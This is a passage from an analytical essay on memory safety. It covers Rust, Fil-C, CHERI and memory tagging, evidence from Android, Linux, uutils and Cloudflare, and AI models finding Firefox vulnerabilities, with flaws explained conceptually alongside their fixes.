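v.push(40);                    // the compiler rejects this line
*first = 11;                   // the borrow lasts until here
```

A growable list in Rust keeps its items in one block on the heap. If the block is full when the program adds an item, the list moves to a larger block and frees the old one. `first` would then point to freed memory, and the last line would be a use-after-free. The compiler rejects the program because `first` borrows the list from the second line to the fourth, while `push` needs exclusive access to it on the third. Without the last line, the program would compile, because the borrow would end before `push` begins.

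All of this happens before the program runs and doesn't slow it down. It also rules out data races, in which two threads (parts of a program that run at the same time) access the same memory without coordinating and at least one of them writes to it. But a position in an array often depends on input, so Rust usually checks at run time that the position is within the array's bounds, as Java does.

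### Enforcement for C programs that already exist

Nobody is going to rewrite billions of lines of C and C++ soon, so researchers have tried to enforce memory safety on the existing code. This is hard because a C pointer is only an address, with no record of which object it belongs to or whether that object still exists.

SoftBound, from 2009, recorded each pointer's bounds in a separate table, and its companion CETS gave every block of memory an identifier that became invalid when the program freed the block. Their designers proved that the pair caught every memory error, provided that every part of the program had the checks. But together they made programs take 116% longer to run on average, and Szekeres and colleagues observe that defences that slow programs by more than about 10% rarely come into wide use.

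Fil-C, a compiler by Filip Pizlo, takes a similar approach much further and doesn't rely on chance. According to Fil-C's *InvisiCaps*, each pointer has two parts: an address, which the C program can read and change as usual, and a hidden record of the object that the pointer may access. The program cannot reach the hidden part. Before each access, the compiled code compares the address with the object's limits. When the program frees an object, Fil-C sets the object's upper limit equal to its lower one, so no address falls within the limits and any later access stops the program. A garbage collector keeps the memory from being reused until no pointers to it remain.

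An early version of Fil-C made programs 200 times slower. The current one makes them about four times slower in bad cases, and structures that contain pointers take up twice the memory. Alden (2025), in *Fil-C*, tried a Fil-C build of Bash, the standard Linux command line, and noticed no difference, because Bash spends most of its time waiting for other programs. Users have to recompile a program together with all its libraries, but most programs need few or no changes. Bernstein has published scripts that set up a variant of Debian Linux with Fil-C.

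CHERI, a project led by the University of Cambridge, moves the check into the processor. *Fitting 192 Bits of Bounds Into 128* (2026) describes the pointer format. A pointer doubles in size to 128 bits, which hold the address, compressed bounds and permissions. One extra bit, stored elsewhere, records whether the pointer is genuine. If a program overwrites a pointer with ordinary data, the processor clears that bit and will no longer follow the pointer. An attacker who replaces a return address with bytes of input therefore crashes the program instead of controlling where it jumps. Because the bounds are compressed, those of some large objects have to be rounded, so the system must leave a gap after these objects.

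CHERI's bounds checks are deterministic, but enforcing lifetimes takes more work. Freeing a block doesn't alter the old pointers to it, so software has to search memory for them and disable them before the program can reuse the block.

How much extra hardware CHERI needs depends on the size of the processor. *An open-source, memory-safe compute subsystem* (Orensanz Martinez, 2026) reports that a very small core takes 57,000 logic gates without protection, 81,000 with ordinary memory protection and 90,000 with CHERI. CHERI adds 57% to the bare core, but only 11% to one that already has ordinary protection. SemiWiki, an industry site, puts the increase at 4–5% in reported implementations, with a modest effect on speed. A bigger obstacle is that CHERI needs new chips. CHERIoT (2025) announced that the first commercial chips based on one small design were on their way back from the factory in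 November 2025, with mass production planned for 2026. The CHERI standard for RISC-V, an open family of processor designs, was close to final in August 2026.

Memory tagging has lower overhead and is already used in phones. Apple's *Memory Integrity Enforcement*, from 2025, describes the version in the iPhone 17. The system gives each block of memory a small secret tag, and each pointer carries the tag of the block it should access. If the two tags differ, the hardware prevents the access. Neighbouring blocks always get different tags, which stops an overflow from one into the next. The system also changes a block's tag when it reuses the memory.

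The Arm design that Apple's builds on has only 16 tags, so a stray pointer to a distant block chosen at random has about a 1 in 16 chance of carrying the right tag. Wrong guesses crash the program and leave a record, but an attacker who can learn the tag doesn't need to guess. Researchers have extracted tags from Google's Pixel phones by measuring tiny timing differences. Apple put much effort, chip area and memory into keeping its tags secret and checking them quickly, but the checks still miss an overflow from one part of a block into another part of the same block.

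Memory tagging is therefore a strong mitigation in the sense used here, despite Apple's name for it. Apple's own attack team could not rebuild any of the earlier spyware attacks it tried against the system. But in May 2026 the security company Calif, with help from Claude Mythos Preview, combined two bugs in five days into an attack that got past the system on a Mac, according to TechRadar's *'This work is a glimpse of what is coming'*.

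### Soundness

A checker is sound if its approval can be trusted completely. For a checker C and a rule φ, such as memory safety, soundness is a theorem of the following form:

**∀P: C(P) = accept ⇒ ∀r ∈ Runs(P): r ⊨ φ**

If the checker accepts a program, every possible run of that program obeys the rule. This holds for every input, including those no attacker has thought of yet. Testing supports a much weaker claim, that the runs somebody tried obeyed the rule.

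With run-time checks, the theorem applies to the program after the compiler has added them. Every run of that program obeys the rule, because a failed check stops the program before it can break the rule.

The formula doesn't include the programmer, so the guarantee is the same whether a person or an AI agent wrote the code. Premise 2, that enforcement removed memory bugs where skill had not, relies on the guarantee being the same for every author.

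A sound checker can reject programs that have no memory bugs, and one that rejected every program would be sound but useless. A program that a sound checker accepts may still not do what its users want. The modified version of qmail that pasted a server's name into a system command would have had the same security hole if it had been written in Java.

### Escape hatches and the trusted base

Rust's basic rule is too strict for some code that programmers need. Several threads may have to update the same data, for example, and an operating system has to talk to hardware at fixed addresses. Rust therefore lets programmers mark a block of code as `unsafe` and use pointers in it that the compiler doesn't track. *Rust in Android* (Vander Stoep, 2025) points out that most of the compiler's other checks still apply inside these blocks, which make up about 4% of Android's Rust code.

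Much of Rust's standard library relies on this escape hatch. Its `Cell` type, for example, lets several references change the same value, which seems to break the rule. This is safe because a program can only get copies of a `Cell`'s contents, never a pointer into it, so changing the value can't leave a pointer dangling. The compiler also keeps references to the same `Cell` within one thread. The compiler can't work out that this design is safe, so the library's developers had to.

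RustBelt was the first formal safety proof for a realistic subset of Rust, including libraries that use unsafe code. The usual proof method assumes a fixed set of rules, but each library with unsafe code in effect adds a new one. Jung and colleagues instead defined, for each type of value, what any code that handles it must guarantee, whether or not the compiler can check that code. They worked in λRust, a simplified model of Rust, and their proof has three parts.

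1. Code that passes the type checker meets the guarantees.
2. If all the code in a program meets the guarantees, no run of the program makes an invalid memory access or has a data race.
3. For each library with unsafe code inside, someone must prove separately that the library meets the guarantees its interface promises.

The first two parts are general theorems, which Jung and colleagues proved once, with a computer checking every step. They then did the third for λRust versions of ten pieces of library code, including `Cell` and the lock that lets threads take turns with shared data. If S is the ordinary code and U₁ to Uₖ are the libraries with unsafe code, the combined result is:

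**C(S) = accept, and U₁, …, Uₖ each meet their guarantees ⇒ every run of S with U₁, …, Uₖ obeys φ**

The third part leaves people with far less to check, because they don't need to examine S at all, however long it is and whoever wrote it. In the earlier arithmetic, if enforcement covers 96% of the risky operations, the expected number of bugs falls by a factor of 25, even if the programmer makes mistakes at the same rate as before.

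Reviewers have to check the whole library that contains an unsafe block, but they can ignore the programs that use the library. For example, a growable list stores its length in a private field, and its unsafe code relies on that length being correct. An ordinary line elsewhere in the library could set the length too high, and the unsafe code would then read past the end of the list's memory.

People do make mistakes in the code that Rust leaves them to check. Researchers found several Rust libraries that each seemed safe alone but were unsafe in combination, and later the work on RustBelt uncovered a new bug in Rust's standard library. In 2025 Android's developers found a buffer overflow in unsafe Rust code that handled images, shortly before it would have reached the public. As a mitigation, Android's memory allocator surrounds large blocks with inaccessible pages, so the overflow caused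 a crash and could not have been exploited.

The guarantee also depends on a trusted base, the components that must work correctly for it to hold. For Rust this includes the compiler, the operating system, the processor and any C code in the same program, since a stray write from C can overwrite Rust's data. Fil-C has no `unsafe` statement, but it still depends on a runtime and a Linux kernel built with an ordinary compiler. RustBelt proves its theorem about λRust, which leaves out some features of the real language, such as the automatic clean-up of values and the faster ways for threads to share data with weaker ordering guarantees.

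A trusted base can be worth having even if it contains bugs, because thousands of programs share it and experts can concentrate on it. But a single bug there can undo the guarantee for all of those programs.

### What made enforcement possible

Memory safety is an unusually convenient rule to enforce, in part because it is precise and identical for every program. Each access must fall inside a block of memory that the program still holds.

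The check also doesn't depend on what the program is for, so the same comparison of a position with a length works in a bank's software and in a game. To prevent the attack on the login flag by protecting only the variables that matter for security, a tool would need to be told that one byte means "logged in" and the next is a screen colour. As Szekeres and colleagues note, which variables are critical depends on the meaning of the program. Memory safety protects every variable from stray writes, so nobody has to identify the critical ones. But because the check doesn't take the program's purpose into account, it can't stop a bank's software from paying the wrong person.

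Programmers also have to put up with a checker that rejects some correct programs. For checks made before the program runs, this follows from Alan Turing's 1936 proof that no general method can determine whether a program will ever finish. Suppose a checker accepted exactly the memory-safe programs. Take any memory-safe program Q, and add a line at the end that writes outside an array. The new program is unsafe only if Q finishes, because otherwise it never reaches that line. The checker would therefore accept the new program exactly when Q runs forever, so we could use it to determine whether any such Q finishes, which Turing proved impossible. A checker that always gives an answer must therefore sometimes be wrong, and if it is sound, meaning it never accepts an unsafe program, its only possible mistake is to reject a safe one.

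This argument doesn't apply to run-time checks, because they test an access just before it happens and don't have to predict anything. They can still be too strict in practice. *Fil's Unbelievable C Compiler* warns that Fil-C's checks may occasionally stop a valid C program.

Programmers have chosen languages according to how much rejected code they will tolerate. Jung and colleagues suggest that earlier research languages with similar goals failed to spread because they either banned too much low-level code or made programmers write proofs to satisfy the checker. Rust combines a simple rule with a way to bypass it for exceptions. If the list in the rejected four-line program had started with room for ten items, adding a fourth would not have moved it and the program would be harmless, but Rust's compiler would still reject it. The programmer can fix it by adding the new item before taking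 the pointer.

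## What happened where enforcement was adopted

Android is the best large test of premise 2, that enforcement removed memory bugs. Around 2019, the Android team began moving new development to memory-safe languages but left most of the existing C and C++ in place. Memory bugs made up 76% of Android's vulnerabilities in 2019 and 24% in 2024. Vander Stoep reports that in 2025 the share fell below 20% for the first time.

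A share can fall because other flaws increase, so the counts matter too. The Hacker News (2025) reports 223 memory vulnerabilities for 2019. Google projected 36 for 2024, based on the 27 it had recorded by September. Dividing each count by its share gives about 293 vulnerabilities of all kinds in 2019 and 150 in 2024. Memory vulnerabilities fell by 84%, while all others rose from about 70 to about 114. Without that rise, the 2024 share would have been 34% instead of 24%, so most of the drop in share came from the fall in memory vulnerabilities.

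*Google Fixes 216 Android Vulnerabilities* (Abdullahi, 2026) reports that Android's November 2026 update alone fixed 216 vulnerabilities, more than the roughly 150 implied for all of 2024. That total covers all kinds of flaws and may include components that Google's series leaves out, so it doesn't show whether memory bugs kept getting rarer. But if a fifth of the 216 were memory bugs, that month would have had more of them than all of 2024, even though their share would be as low as ever.

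### Why the number fell while the old code stayed

Google's explanation is that people gradually find and fix the flaws in old code. A large program stays full of memory bugs only because programmers keep adding new ones.

Suppose that people always find and fix the same fraction of the remaining vulnerabilities each year. If a vulnerability lasts L years on average, the vulnerability density (the number of vulnerabilities per million lines) falls like this:

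**density after t years = starting density × e^(−t/L)**

Google estimates that the average lifetime of a vulnerability, L, is 2.5 years in its own projects. After five years, the fraction remaining is e^(−5/2.5), or about 0.135, so five-year-old code has 7.4 times fewer vulnerabilities per line than when it was new.

Suppose a company's programmers introduce 100 memory vulnerabilities a year and fix 100 a year. If each lasts 2.5 years on average, the code contains 250 at any moment. The programmers then switch to a language that prevents new ones. Five years later, 34 are left and the company is fixing about 14 a year, even though nobody has rewritten any of the old code.

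Google's simulation models a more gradual change, in which new development takes ten years to move to memory-safe languages, slowly at first, then quickly, then slowly again. It assumes that the code doubles in size every six years, that vulnerabilities last 2.5 years on average, and that programmers change old code only to fix bugs. By the end, the program contains more memory-unsafe code than at the start, but far fewer memory vulnerabilities, because most of the unsafe code is old.

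The exponential curve comes from *How Long Do Vulnerabilities Live in the Code?* (Alexopoulos, Brack and colleagues, 2022), which estimated how long vulnerabilities had lasted in 11 open-source projects written mainly in C and C++, using more than 5,000 that developers had since fixed. An exponential distribution fitted well for lifetimes of up to about 5,000 days, which covered 98% of the data. The average lifetime was about four years, which makes the density of vulnerabilities in five-year-old code only 3.4 times lower than in new code. Projects differed widely, and after five years 9% of the original vulnerabilities would remain at the average lifetime for Chromium, the browser project behind Chrome, compared with half at the average for OpenSSL, an encryption library.

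In these projects, the average age of the vulnerabilities that developers fixed also rose by about 43 days each year. Alexopoulos and colleagues think this was probably because developers were adding vulnerabilities at least as fast as they fixed them. If developers had instead been running out of new flaws and working through the old ones, the distribution of ages would have changed shape, but it stayed exponential. Modern fuzzing tools did not noticeably shorten the life of memory bugs in Linux either. This fits Google's view that the supply of new bugs matters most.

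But the model probably underestimates how many bugs remain in old code. A bug that nobody has found has no recorded lifetime, so the 29-year-old error in Postfix would have been missing from any average of bug lifetimes until 2026. Growth also makes the average look too short, because a program that doubles in size every six years contains much more young code than old, so the bugs that people fix are mostly young too. If Google's 2.5 years is the average age of fixed bugs in a program growing that fast, the true average lifetime is about 3.5 years, and five-year-old code still has about a quarter as many bugs per line as new code.

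Android's memory bugs also fell faster than the model predicts under realistic assumptions. The number found each year dropped from 223 to 36 in five years, a factor of 6.2. With L = 2.5, the model predicts a factor of 7.4 if programmers had stopped adding memory bugs completely in 2019, but they hadn't. Google's own developers added far more C++ than Rust until 2022, and about as much C++ as Rust in 2024. If the supply of new memory bugs had fallen steadily to half its 2019 level by 2024, the model predicts that yearly discoveries would have fallen by about 28%, not 84%. Google noticed that its real results were better than its simulation, and suggested that parallel work on the safety of its C and C++ code might be one reason. So safe languages probably caused only part of the drop, and we can't work out from the yearly totals how large that part was. Comparing code by language gives a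 better estimate.

### One near-miss in five million lines

In 2025, Android's developers caught an overflow in CrabbyAVIF, a library that decodes a type of compressed image. The overflow was nearly the first memory vulnerability in Android's Rust code to reach the public. Google gave it an identifier, CVE-2025-48530, so that the fix would get high priority and staff could track it through each release.

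The overflow wrote one byte after another past the end of its block until it reached one of the inaccessible pages that Scudo, Android's default memory allocator, puts around large blocks. The crash helped developers notice the bug, but the crash report didn't make clear that an overflow was the cause, which slowed the diagnosis. Not every Android device uses Scudo. Google is working with its partners to make it mandatory, and in the meantime still issues CVE numbers for serious bugs that Scudo would stop.

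Vander Stoep uses this bug to estimate a density of 0.2 vulnerabilities per million lines of Rust, or one in roughly 5 million lines. Google's historical figure for Android's C and C++ is about 1,000 per million lines, which is 5,000 times as high. Vander Stoep cautiously reports the reduction as more than 1,000 times.

A rate based on one event is very uncertain. If memory vulnerabilities turn up independently at a steady rate, finding one gives a 95% confidence interval of 0.025 to 5.6 for the true average. That is 0.005 to 1.1 per million lines, so Rust's density could be about 900 to 200,000 times lower than that of C and C++, which is a very large improvement even at the low end.

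The youth of the Rust code is a more serious problem, because people have had less time to find its flaws. Most of it dates from 2023 or later. If it averaged two years old and flaws lasted 2.5 years on average, people would have found only 55% of them. If flaws lasted almost nine years, the longest average in the study by Alexopoulos and colleagues, people would have found about a fifth. But the gap between the languages is so wide that this hardly changes the conclusion. Even if people had found only one in twenty, the Rust code would have 4 vulnerabilities per million lines, still 250 times fewer than C and C++.

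Android's Rust code may also do different work from its C and C++ code. The C and C++ code includes many old components that attackers have studied for years, and bug hunters may spend less time on Rust because they expect to find little there. To remove these doubts, someone would have to write the same components in both languages and have the same people attack them. But such differences seem unlikely to account for a factor of hundreds.

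About 4% of the 5 million lines, or 200,000 lines, are unsafe Rust. If they were as error-prone as C and C++, they would contain about 200 memory vulnerabilities, but Google has found one. Vander Stoep isn't sure why unsafe Rust does so well. He suggests it helps that the compiler still makes most of its checks, and that programmers enclose unsafe code in small units they can reason about separately and review it with extra care. So human care, concentrated on a small part of the code, probably partly explains the low density of vulnerabilities.

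### Rust's effect on the pace of development

In Android, stricter checking seems to speed programmers up once a change reaches review, contrary to the long-held assumption that it slows them down. Rust changes need about 20% fewer revisions than C++ changes of similar size and spend about 25% less time in code review. Developers also roll back (withdraw after accepting) medium and large Rust changes about a quarter as often as C++ ones.

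Google compared only changes by its own Android developers, many of whom write both Rust and C++. But it didn't assign the languages at random. A developer who writes a new component in Rust may have an easier job than one who alters a fifteen-year-old C++ component that much of the system relies on, and we would expect easier work to be rolled back less often. The measurements also leave out the time programmers spend satisfying the compiler before they submit a change.

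Most of the gain in review time appeared between 2023 and 2024. Vander Stoep speculates that the team was becoming more expert in Rust during that period. If so, a team new to Rust shouldn't expect the same gain in its first year. The results are good evidence that enforcement needn't be a heavy burden on development, but weaker evidence that it makes a given programmer faster.

### Rust in the Linux kernel

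The Linux kernel is a less clear-cut case. Its developers now accept some code in Rust, and Google first enabled Rust in Android's version 6.12 kernel. The first CVE for Rust code in Linux came on 16 December 2025. OSV's *CVE-2025-68260* (2025) traces the flaw to the Rust rewrite of Binder, the driver that passes messages between parts of Android.

The bug was a data race. Rust's compiler rules these out in ordinary code, but this one happened in an unsafe operation, where the programmer has to prevent them. The operation removes an item from a list, and is safe only if no other thread is changing the item's pointers at the same time. The programmer had argued in a comment that this condition held because an item never enters the list of any node except its owner. The argument was wrong because the driver elsewhere moved items onto a temporary list and then released the lock that protected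 them, so two threads could change the same pointers at once and corrupt them.

Sources differ on how serious the bug is. OSV rates it 7.8 out of 10, or "High", which allows for stolen data and altered files as well as crashes. Red Hat's *Bug 2422751 (CVE-2025-68260)* (2025) rates it medium. It's FOSS's *The First Rust CVE in Linux Kernel Only Makes Your System Crash* describes only a crash.

According to the same article, the kernel team announced this CVE alongside more than 150 for C code. Those counts alone can't show whether Rust has fewer CVEs per line than C. Tom's Hardware's *Linux kernel nears record 2,000 vulnerabilities per release* puts the kernel at 40 million lines. If Rust made up one line in 150, or about 270,000 lines, then one CVE in 150 would be proportional to its share of the code. The batch is also an unfair sample, because people singled it out for containing the first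 Rust CVE.

The kernel team also assigns CVE numbers freely. Any fix for a weakness that affects confidentiality, integrity or availability can receive one, according to SC Media's *Linux kernel security faces challenge with surge in CVEs* (2026), and in July 2026 the team published 432 in two days. Outside the kernel, the standard for what counts as a vulnerability can be stricter for Rust than for C. People often report a vulnerability in a Rust library if some safe program could use it to cause a memory error, even if no existing program does. without.boats' *What constitutes a vulnerability?* argues that C would have a practically infinite number of CVEs by that standard. Even an ordinary C array access lets a careless caller break memory safety.

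The kernel's first recorded Rust vulnerability arose where the compiler's check was off, which is where the theory predicts that memory bugs will survive. There isn't yet enough evidence to estimate how rare such bugs will be.

### What memory-safe programs still get wrong

In late 2025, Ubuntu, a popular version of Linux, replaced the coreutils, one of the most heavily used sets of C programs, with a Rust rewrite called uutils. The coreutils are the basic commands that copy, delete and list files, and thousands of scripts depend on them. Canonical, the company behind Ubuntu, hired the security firm Zellic to audit the rewrite. Ubuntu's *An update on rust-coreutils* reports 113 issues over two rounds. The first round found 73, of which Zellic rated seven critical and 11 high, according to its summary as relayed in Coopersmith (2026), *Security audit of rust-coreutils*. Canonical disclosed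 44 CVEs.

None of the 44 flaws that Zellic found in the rewrite was a buffer overflow or a use-after-free, as corrode's *Bugs Rust Won't Catch* points out. The GNU version, which is written in C, has had several such bugs fixed in recent years, including one in 2026, an overflow that occurred when `pwd` printed the name of a very deeply nested folder. An audit can miss things, so this doesn't prove that the rewrite has no memory bugs.

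Many were races over file names. The `install` command, which puts a file in place and often runs as administrator, included two steps like these:

```rust
fs::remove_file(to)?;              // delete the old file
let mut dest = File::create(to)?;  // create a new one by that name
```

Between the two steps, an attacker who can write to the same folder creates a link with the name that `install` is about to use and points it at the system's password file. `File::create` follows the link, and the command overwrites the password file, even though both lines are memory-safe. The fix is also a form of enforcement, but of a rule other than memory safety. The program asks the operating system to create the file only if nothing by that name exists, and the operating system checks this as part of creating the file, so the attacker has no gap to use.

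Other flaws came from rules the programmers had stated too narrowly. The `chmod` command has a safeguard against changing the permissions of every file on the computer. It checked only whether the folder's name was `/`, the top folder, so it missed `/../`, another name for the same folder. In the GNU version, `kill -1` specifies a type of signal, and the user must then name a program to send it to. The rewrite treated `kill -1` as an instruction to end every program the user could see.

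The worst flaw gave an attacker complete control. It was in `chroot`, a command that confines a program to one part of the file system. The rewritten command entered that part before looking up the user who should run the program. The lookup can load code from files there, and `chroot` was still running as administrator, so an attacker who had planted a file could run any code as administrator. The GNU version looks up the user before entering.

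Rewriting the commands brought some of these problems back. The GNU programs are about 40 years old, and their developers had fixed many such mistakes long ago. According to corrode, Rust's standard library also made the file races easier to write, because its most convenient functions look up a file by name each time, while C programmers more often keep using a file they have already opened. Canonical kept the GNU versions of `cp`, `mv` and `rm` in Ubuntu 26.04 because of the races. Funk (2026), in *uutils coreutils CVEs*, still found three of the disclosed flaws in a fully updated copy of that release. Funk helps develop the GNU version and admits to perhaps overestimating the flaws' importance.

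The decay model gives companies a reason to leave old C code alone, since much of it has already lost most of its flaws and a rewrite would introduce new ones. This reason doesn't apply to a new program, which has no old code to replace.

Crashes also remain, and some do great damage. On 18 November 2025, Cloudflare, which carries traffic for a large part of the web, had its worst outage since 2019. It began when engineers changed the permissions on a database, which caused a query to return duplicate rows (Prince, 2025, *Cloudflare outage on November 18, 2025*). The query built a configuration file listing the features that a machine-learning model uses to recognise automated visitors. The file normally listed about 60 features, and the software had reserved memory for up to 200. The duplicates pushed the file over that limit.

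The newer version of Cloudflare's software, written in Rust, checked the number of features and correctly produced an error. But the programmer had called `unwrap()` on the result, which continues if the operation worked and stops the program if it failed. The program stopped, and websites that relied on it showed error pages. Most traffic was back to normal by 14:30, about three hours after the trouble began.

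Stopping was safer than writing past the end of the reserved memory, as an unchecked C program might have done, but a better program would have kept using the previous file. Rust requires programmers to handle a possible error before using the result, but it lets them do so by stopping the program.

Cloudflare's older software also failed that day, but without crashing. It gave every visitor a score of zero, which marked them as automated, so customers who blocked automated visitors would have turned away many real people. Whether a wrong score is worse than an error page depends on the customer, and a memory-safety check can't determine that. A shop may prefer the wrong score, while a site under attack may not.

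### Why adoption took decades

Bounds checking, the technique that stops buffer overflows, is older than C. The British computer scientist Tony Hoare designed an ALGOL 60 compiler at a small computer manufacturer, which delivered it in 1963. Programs compiled with it checked the bounds on every array access.

Years later the company asked its customers whether they wanted to switch the checks off to make finished programs faster. In his Turing Award lecture, *The Emperor's Old Clothes*, Hoare (1980) recalled that they unanimously said no, because they already knew how often such errors occurred in real use and how disastrous an undetected one could be. He complained that even in 1980, "language designers and users have not learned this lesson", and added that in any respectable branch of engineering, leaving out such a precaution would have been illegal long ago.

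Part of the delay had a technical cause. Hoare's checks couldn't catch a use-after-free, and for decades the main dependable way to prevent one was garbage collection, which was rarely practical in kernels and drivers. Rust, the first widely used language to enforce both bounds and lifetimes without a garbage collector, had its first stable release only in 2015. Full enforcement with acceptable overhead has therefore been available for operating systems for only about a decade. This doesn't explain the delay in adopting bounds checks, which C programmers could have used all along.

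Speed and memory were also scarcer. Hoare describes machines on which a program one word too long could not run. C's designers wanted a small, fast language for such machines, which was a reasonable aim in the 1970s. It became less reasonable as computers grew faster and began to receive data from strangers over networks, but by then much software and many programmers' habits depended on C.

Who bears the harm from an error probably mattered as well. Hoare's customers ran the programs they compiled, so the checks slowed them down, but an undetected error would also have hurt them. The maker of a mass-market program has an incentive to put speed first. Buyers notice if the program is slow but can't easily see whether it has memory bugs, and they bear much of the loss if someone breaks in years later. The contest that Parker and colleagues studied gave teams a similar incentive.

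This can't be the whole explanation, because people who are harmed by errors don't always ask for stricter rules. Hoare's customers had refused to give up bounds checks because they valued protection from an error that had already hurt them. But they also wanted to stop declaring the names of their variables, even though declarations catch spelling mistakes. In 1963 Hoare passed the request on to the committee in charge of ALGOL, which politely rejected it. He later agreed that a language should make as many errors as possible impossible or easy to detect before the program runs.

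Existing code was perhaps the largest obstacle. If memory safety had meant rewriting everything, hardly any company could have afforded it. The Android team avoided a full rewrite by changing only how it wrote new code and by making it easier to use Rust and C++ together in one program. That approach still leaves old code exposed for years, including in dangerous places such as a phone's modem, which connects it to the mobile network. Google's *Bringing Rust to the Pixel Baseband* describes adding one Rust component to the Pixel 10's modem. The component reads replies from the system that turns names into network addresses, and those replies can come from strangers. The modem has tens of megabytes of other code, most of it memory-unsafe. In Help Net Security's *Google makes it harder to exploit Pixel 10 modem firmware*, a Google engineer says that this code may still contain critical memory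 vulnerabilities.

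## Do AI programmers change the verdict?

Premise 1 rests on human programmers' error rates, and AI systems may do better. They already match or beat most experts at finding security flaws. Cable, who has reported hundreds of vulnerabilities, says in *The AI bugpocalypse is here. Now what?* (2026) that models are now significantly better at finding them. In ISRG's *Vulnerabilities and Best Practices in an LLM World* (2026), Josh Aas doubts that human researchers would be more effective at reducing the flaws in a program.

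The evidence from 2026 shows that AI can remove memory bugs from existing code much faster than people did, but it doesn't yet show that AI can write C without adding new ones.

### What AI found in Firefox

Firefox is a hard test because its developer, Mozilla, had already tried nearly everything else, including years of fuzzing, an internal team of attackers and Rust for some components. In a typical month of 2025, Mozilla fixed 20 to 30 security bugs. In April 2026 it fixed 423, according to Mozilla's *Behind the Scenes Hardening Firefox with Claude Mythos Preview* (2026). Anthropic's Mythos Preview model found 271 of them, all fixed in Firefox 150. Outside researchers reported 41. Mozilla found the other 111, about a third each with the same model, other models and older methods such as fuzzing.

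Mozilla had tried earlier models, such as GPT-4, but they raised too many false alarms. The newer system tells the model that a certain part of the code has a bug and asks it to prove it with a test case. The model writes a test, runs it, and tries again if the test doesn't trigger the bug. Mozilla runs many copies at once, each working on one file. Engineers then remove duplicates, judge how serious each bug is, and write the fix.

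Most of the 271 were probably memory bugs, though Mozilla gives no exact count. It grouped the bugs found internally for Firefox 150 into three public entries covering 316 bugs. GCVE's *CVE-2026-6784* (2026) lists the largest as "Memory safety bugs", and AhnLab's *Mozilla Product Security Update Advisory* describes the other two the same way. The label is loose, since the largest entry reports evidence of memory corruption for only "some" of its bugs. Of the 12 sample reports Mozilla also published, five describe a use-after-free and one describes a read past the end of a buffer. Two more describe bugs that would let an attacker pass off other data as an object, which can allow the attacker to read and write memory at will.

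One of the sample bugs was a 20-year-old mistake in the code for XSLT, a language for transforming documents. While the browser was using an entry in a table, a document could make it look up another entry, which could move the table to a new block of memory and free the old one. The browser then kept using a pointer to the old block. This is the same mistake as in the growable list example that Rust's compiler rejected earlier. Fuzzers had missed another bug for years, though a very small web page could trigger it with a table of more than 65,535 rows, which overflowed a 16-bit number.

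Mozilla rated 180 of the 271 bugs as high severity, 80 as moderate and 11 as low. It bases a high rating on symptoms such as a use-after-free, without building an attack. Firefox also runs each website in a sandboxed process that an attacker would have to escape, so a high rating doesn't mean that someone could have taken over a computer with that bug alone.

Several researchers had previously escaped the sandbox by tampering with prototypes, shared JavaScript objects from which other objects inherit their behaviour. Instead of fixing each case, Mozilla froze the prototypes in the privileged part of the browser so that nothing could alter them. According to its logs, the models tried this route many times and failed. But the sample reports also include an escape from RLBox, which confines third-party libraries inside Firefox. The model found a gap in the code that checks values as they leave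 the confined part. Enforcement therefore withstood an expert-level attacker where the prototypes were frozen, but failed in RLBox because of a mistake in the trusted base.

### Is the supply of bugs running out?

Mozilla thinks the supply of bugs can be exhausted. *The zero-days are numbered*, which announced the 271 fixes, says "The defects are finite". Until now, attackers could spend months of expert effort finding one bug that automated tools had missed, while defenders had to find them all. If machines can find every bug that a person can, attackers lose that advantage. Mozilla had seen no type of bug that people could find and the model couldn't. It had also seen none that an elite human researcher couldn't have found, which suggests that better models won't keep uncovering strange new kinds.

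This is a good argument that the number of bugs in one version of Firefox is finite. But it doesn't show how large that number is, and Firefox changes all the time. In May, Mozilla said it hadn't yet found them all.

AI scanning still hadn't cleared Firefox of memory bugs by autumn. Of the first 21 entries in Mozilla's 13 October advisory, *Security Vulnerabilities fixed in Firefox 158* (2026), 15 are use-after-free or bounds errors. In November OpenAI said that its GPT-6 Cyber model had helped find 81 previously unknown flaws in Firefox, according to The Hacker News' *OpenAI Launches GPT-6 Cyber After AI Helps Find 81 Firefox Flaws* (2026). Mozilla rated them high severity, as EconoTimes' *GPT-6 Cyber Identified 81 Previously Unknown Firefox Vulnerabilities, OpenAI Says* (2026) reports. By then, Firefox had been scanned with other strong models for more than half a year.

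The totals are harder to interpret. TecStudio's *Firefox 159 corrige 167 falhas de segurança descobertas com IA da OpenAI* (2026) reports 167 security fixes in Firefox 159, which came out about two weeks after Firefox 158. If that count is right and the pace continued, Mozilla would fix more than 300 a month, not far below April's peak. But one release doesn't establish a trend, and totals are hard to compare over time because Firefox moved to faster releases in September and Mozilla now publishes a separate entry for every memory bug it finds itself. Braun and Kerschbaumer (2026), in *Firefox Security & Privacy Newsletter 2026 Q3*, warn that such counts are not a reliable measure of security.

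The overlap between two searches would be a better guide to how many bugs a program contains. Suppose one model finds 300 bugs and another, working independently on the same version, finds 100. If 75 of those 100 are among the 300, the first model seems to have found about three-quarters of the bugs, which implies a total of around 400. If only 10 are, the implied total is 3,000. We can't use OpenAI's figure this way because it leaves out the bugs Mozilla already knew about.

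Even a large overlap could make the search look more complete than it is, because models trained on similar material probably find the same bugs easily and miss the same ones.

### The repair backlog

Finding a bug protects nobody until someone fixes it. Mozilla could handle 423 fixes in a month because more than 100 people contributed code. Other large companies are also fixing bugs faster. Anthropic reports that one release from the security company Palo Alto Networks had over five times as many patches as usual.

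Smaller projects are struggling to patch the flaws that AI finds. Anthropic has used Mythos Preview to scan more than 1,000 open-source projects and keeps a public record of the results. According to an early count in The Next Web, reviewers had confirmed 1,094 flaws of high or critical severity, but developers had patched only 97.

These figures cover flaws of every kind, not only memory bugs, and the ledger may be unreliable. VulnCheck, a security firm that reviewed the ledger after five months, found many discrepancies in Anthropic's published data, which still covered only a small fraction of the findings. The firm does agree that AI is very useful for finding vulnerabilities, and bookkeeping problems alone are unlikely to explain a gap this wide.

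Most of the work seems to be assessing the reports. Stenberg (2026), in *High volume AI vulnerability reports*, says that each report to curl, a widely used tool for transferring data, takes hours to days to assess, while the fix is usually quick. If assessment took one working day on average, 5,000 reports would need more than 20 person-years. If the reports were spread evenly over 1,000 projects, each project would need about five days, but they won't be spread evenly. Even five days, which a company could easily spare, may be too much for a volunteer who maintains a library in the evenings.

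AI can probably shrink this backlog too. OpenAI sent Mozilla suggested fixes along with its 81 findings, and a model that can demonstrate a bug can often test whether a change removes it. Assessment will very likely get faster. But a maintainer still has to decide whether to trust the change, and models remain weaker at judgments that depend on context. Aas notes that they often misjudge how serious or exploitable a bug is.

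### Attackers can use the fixes

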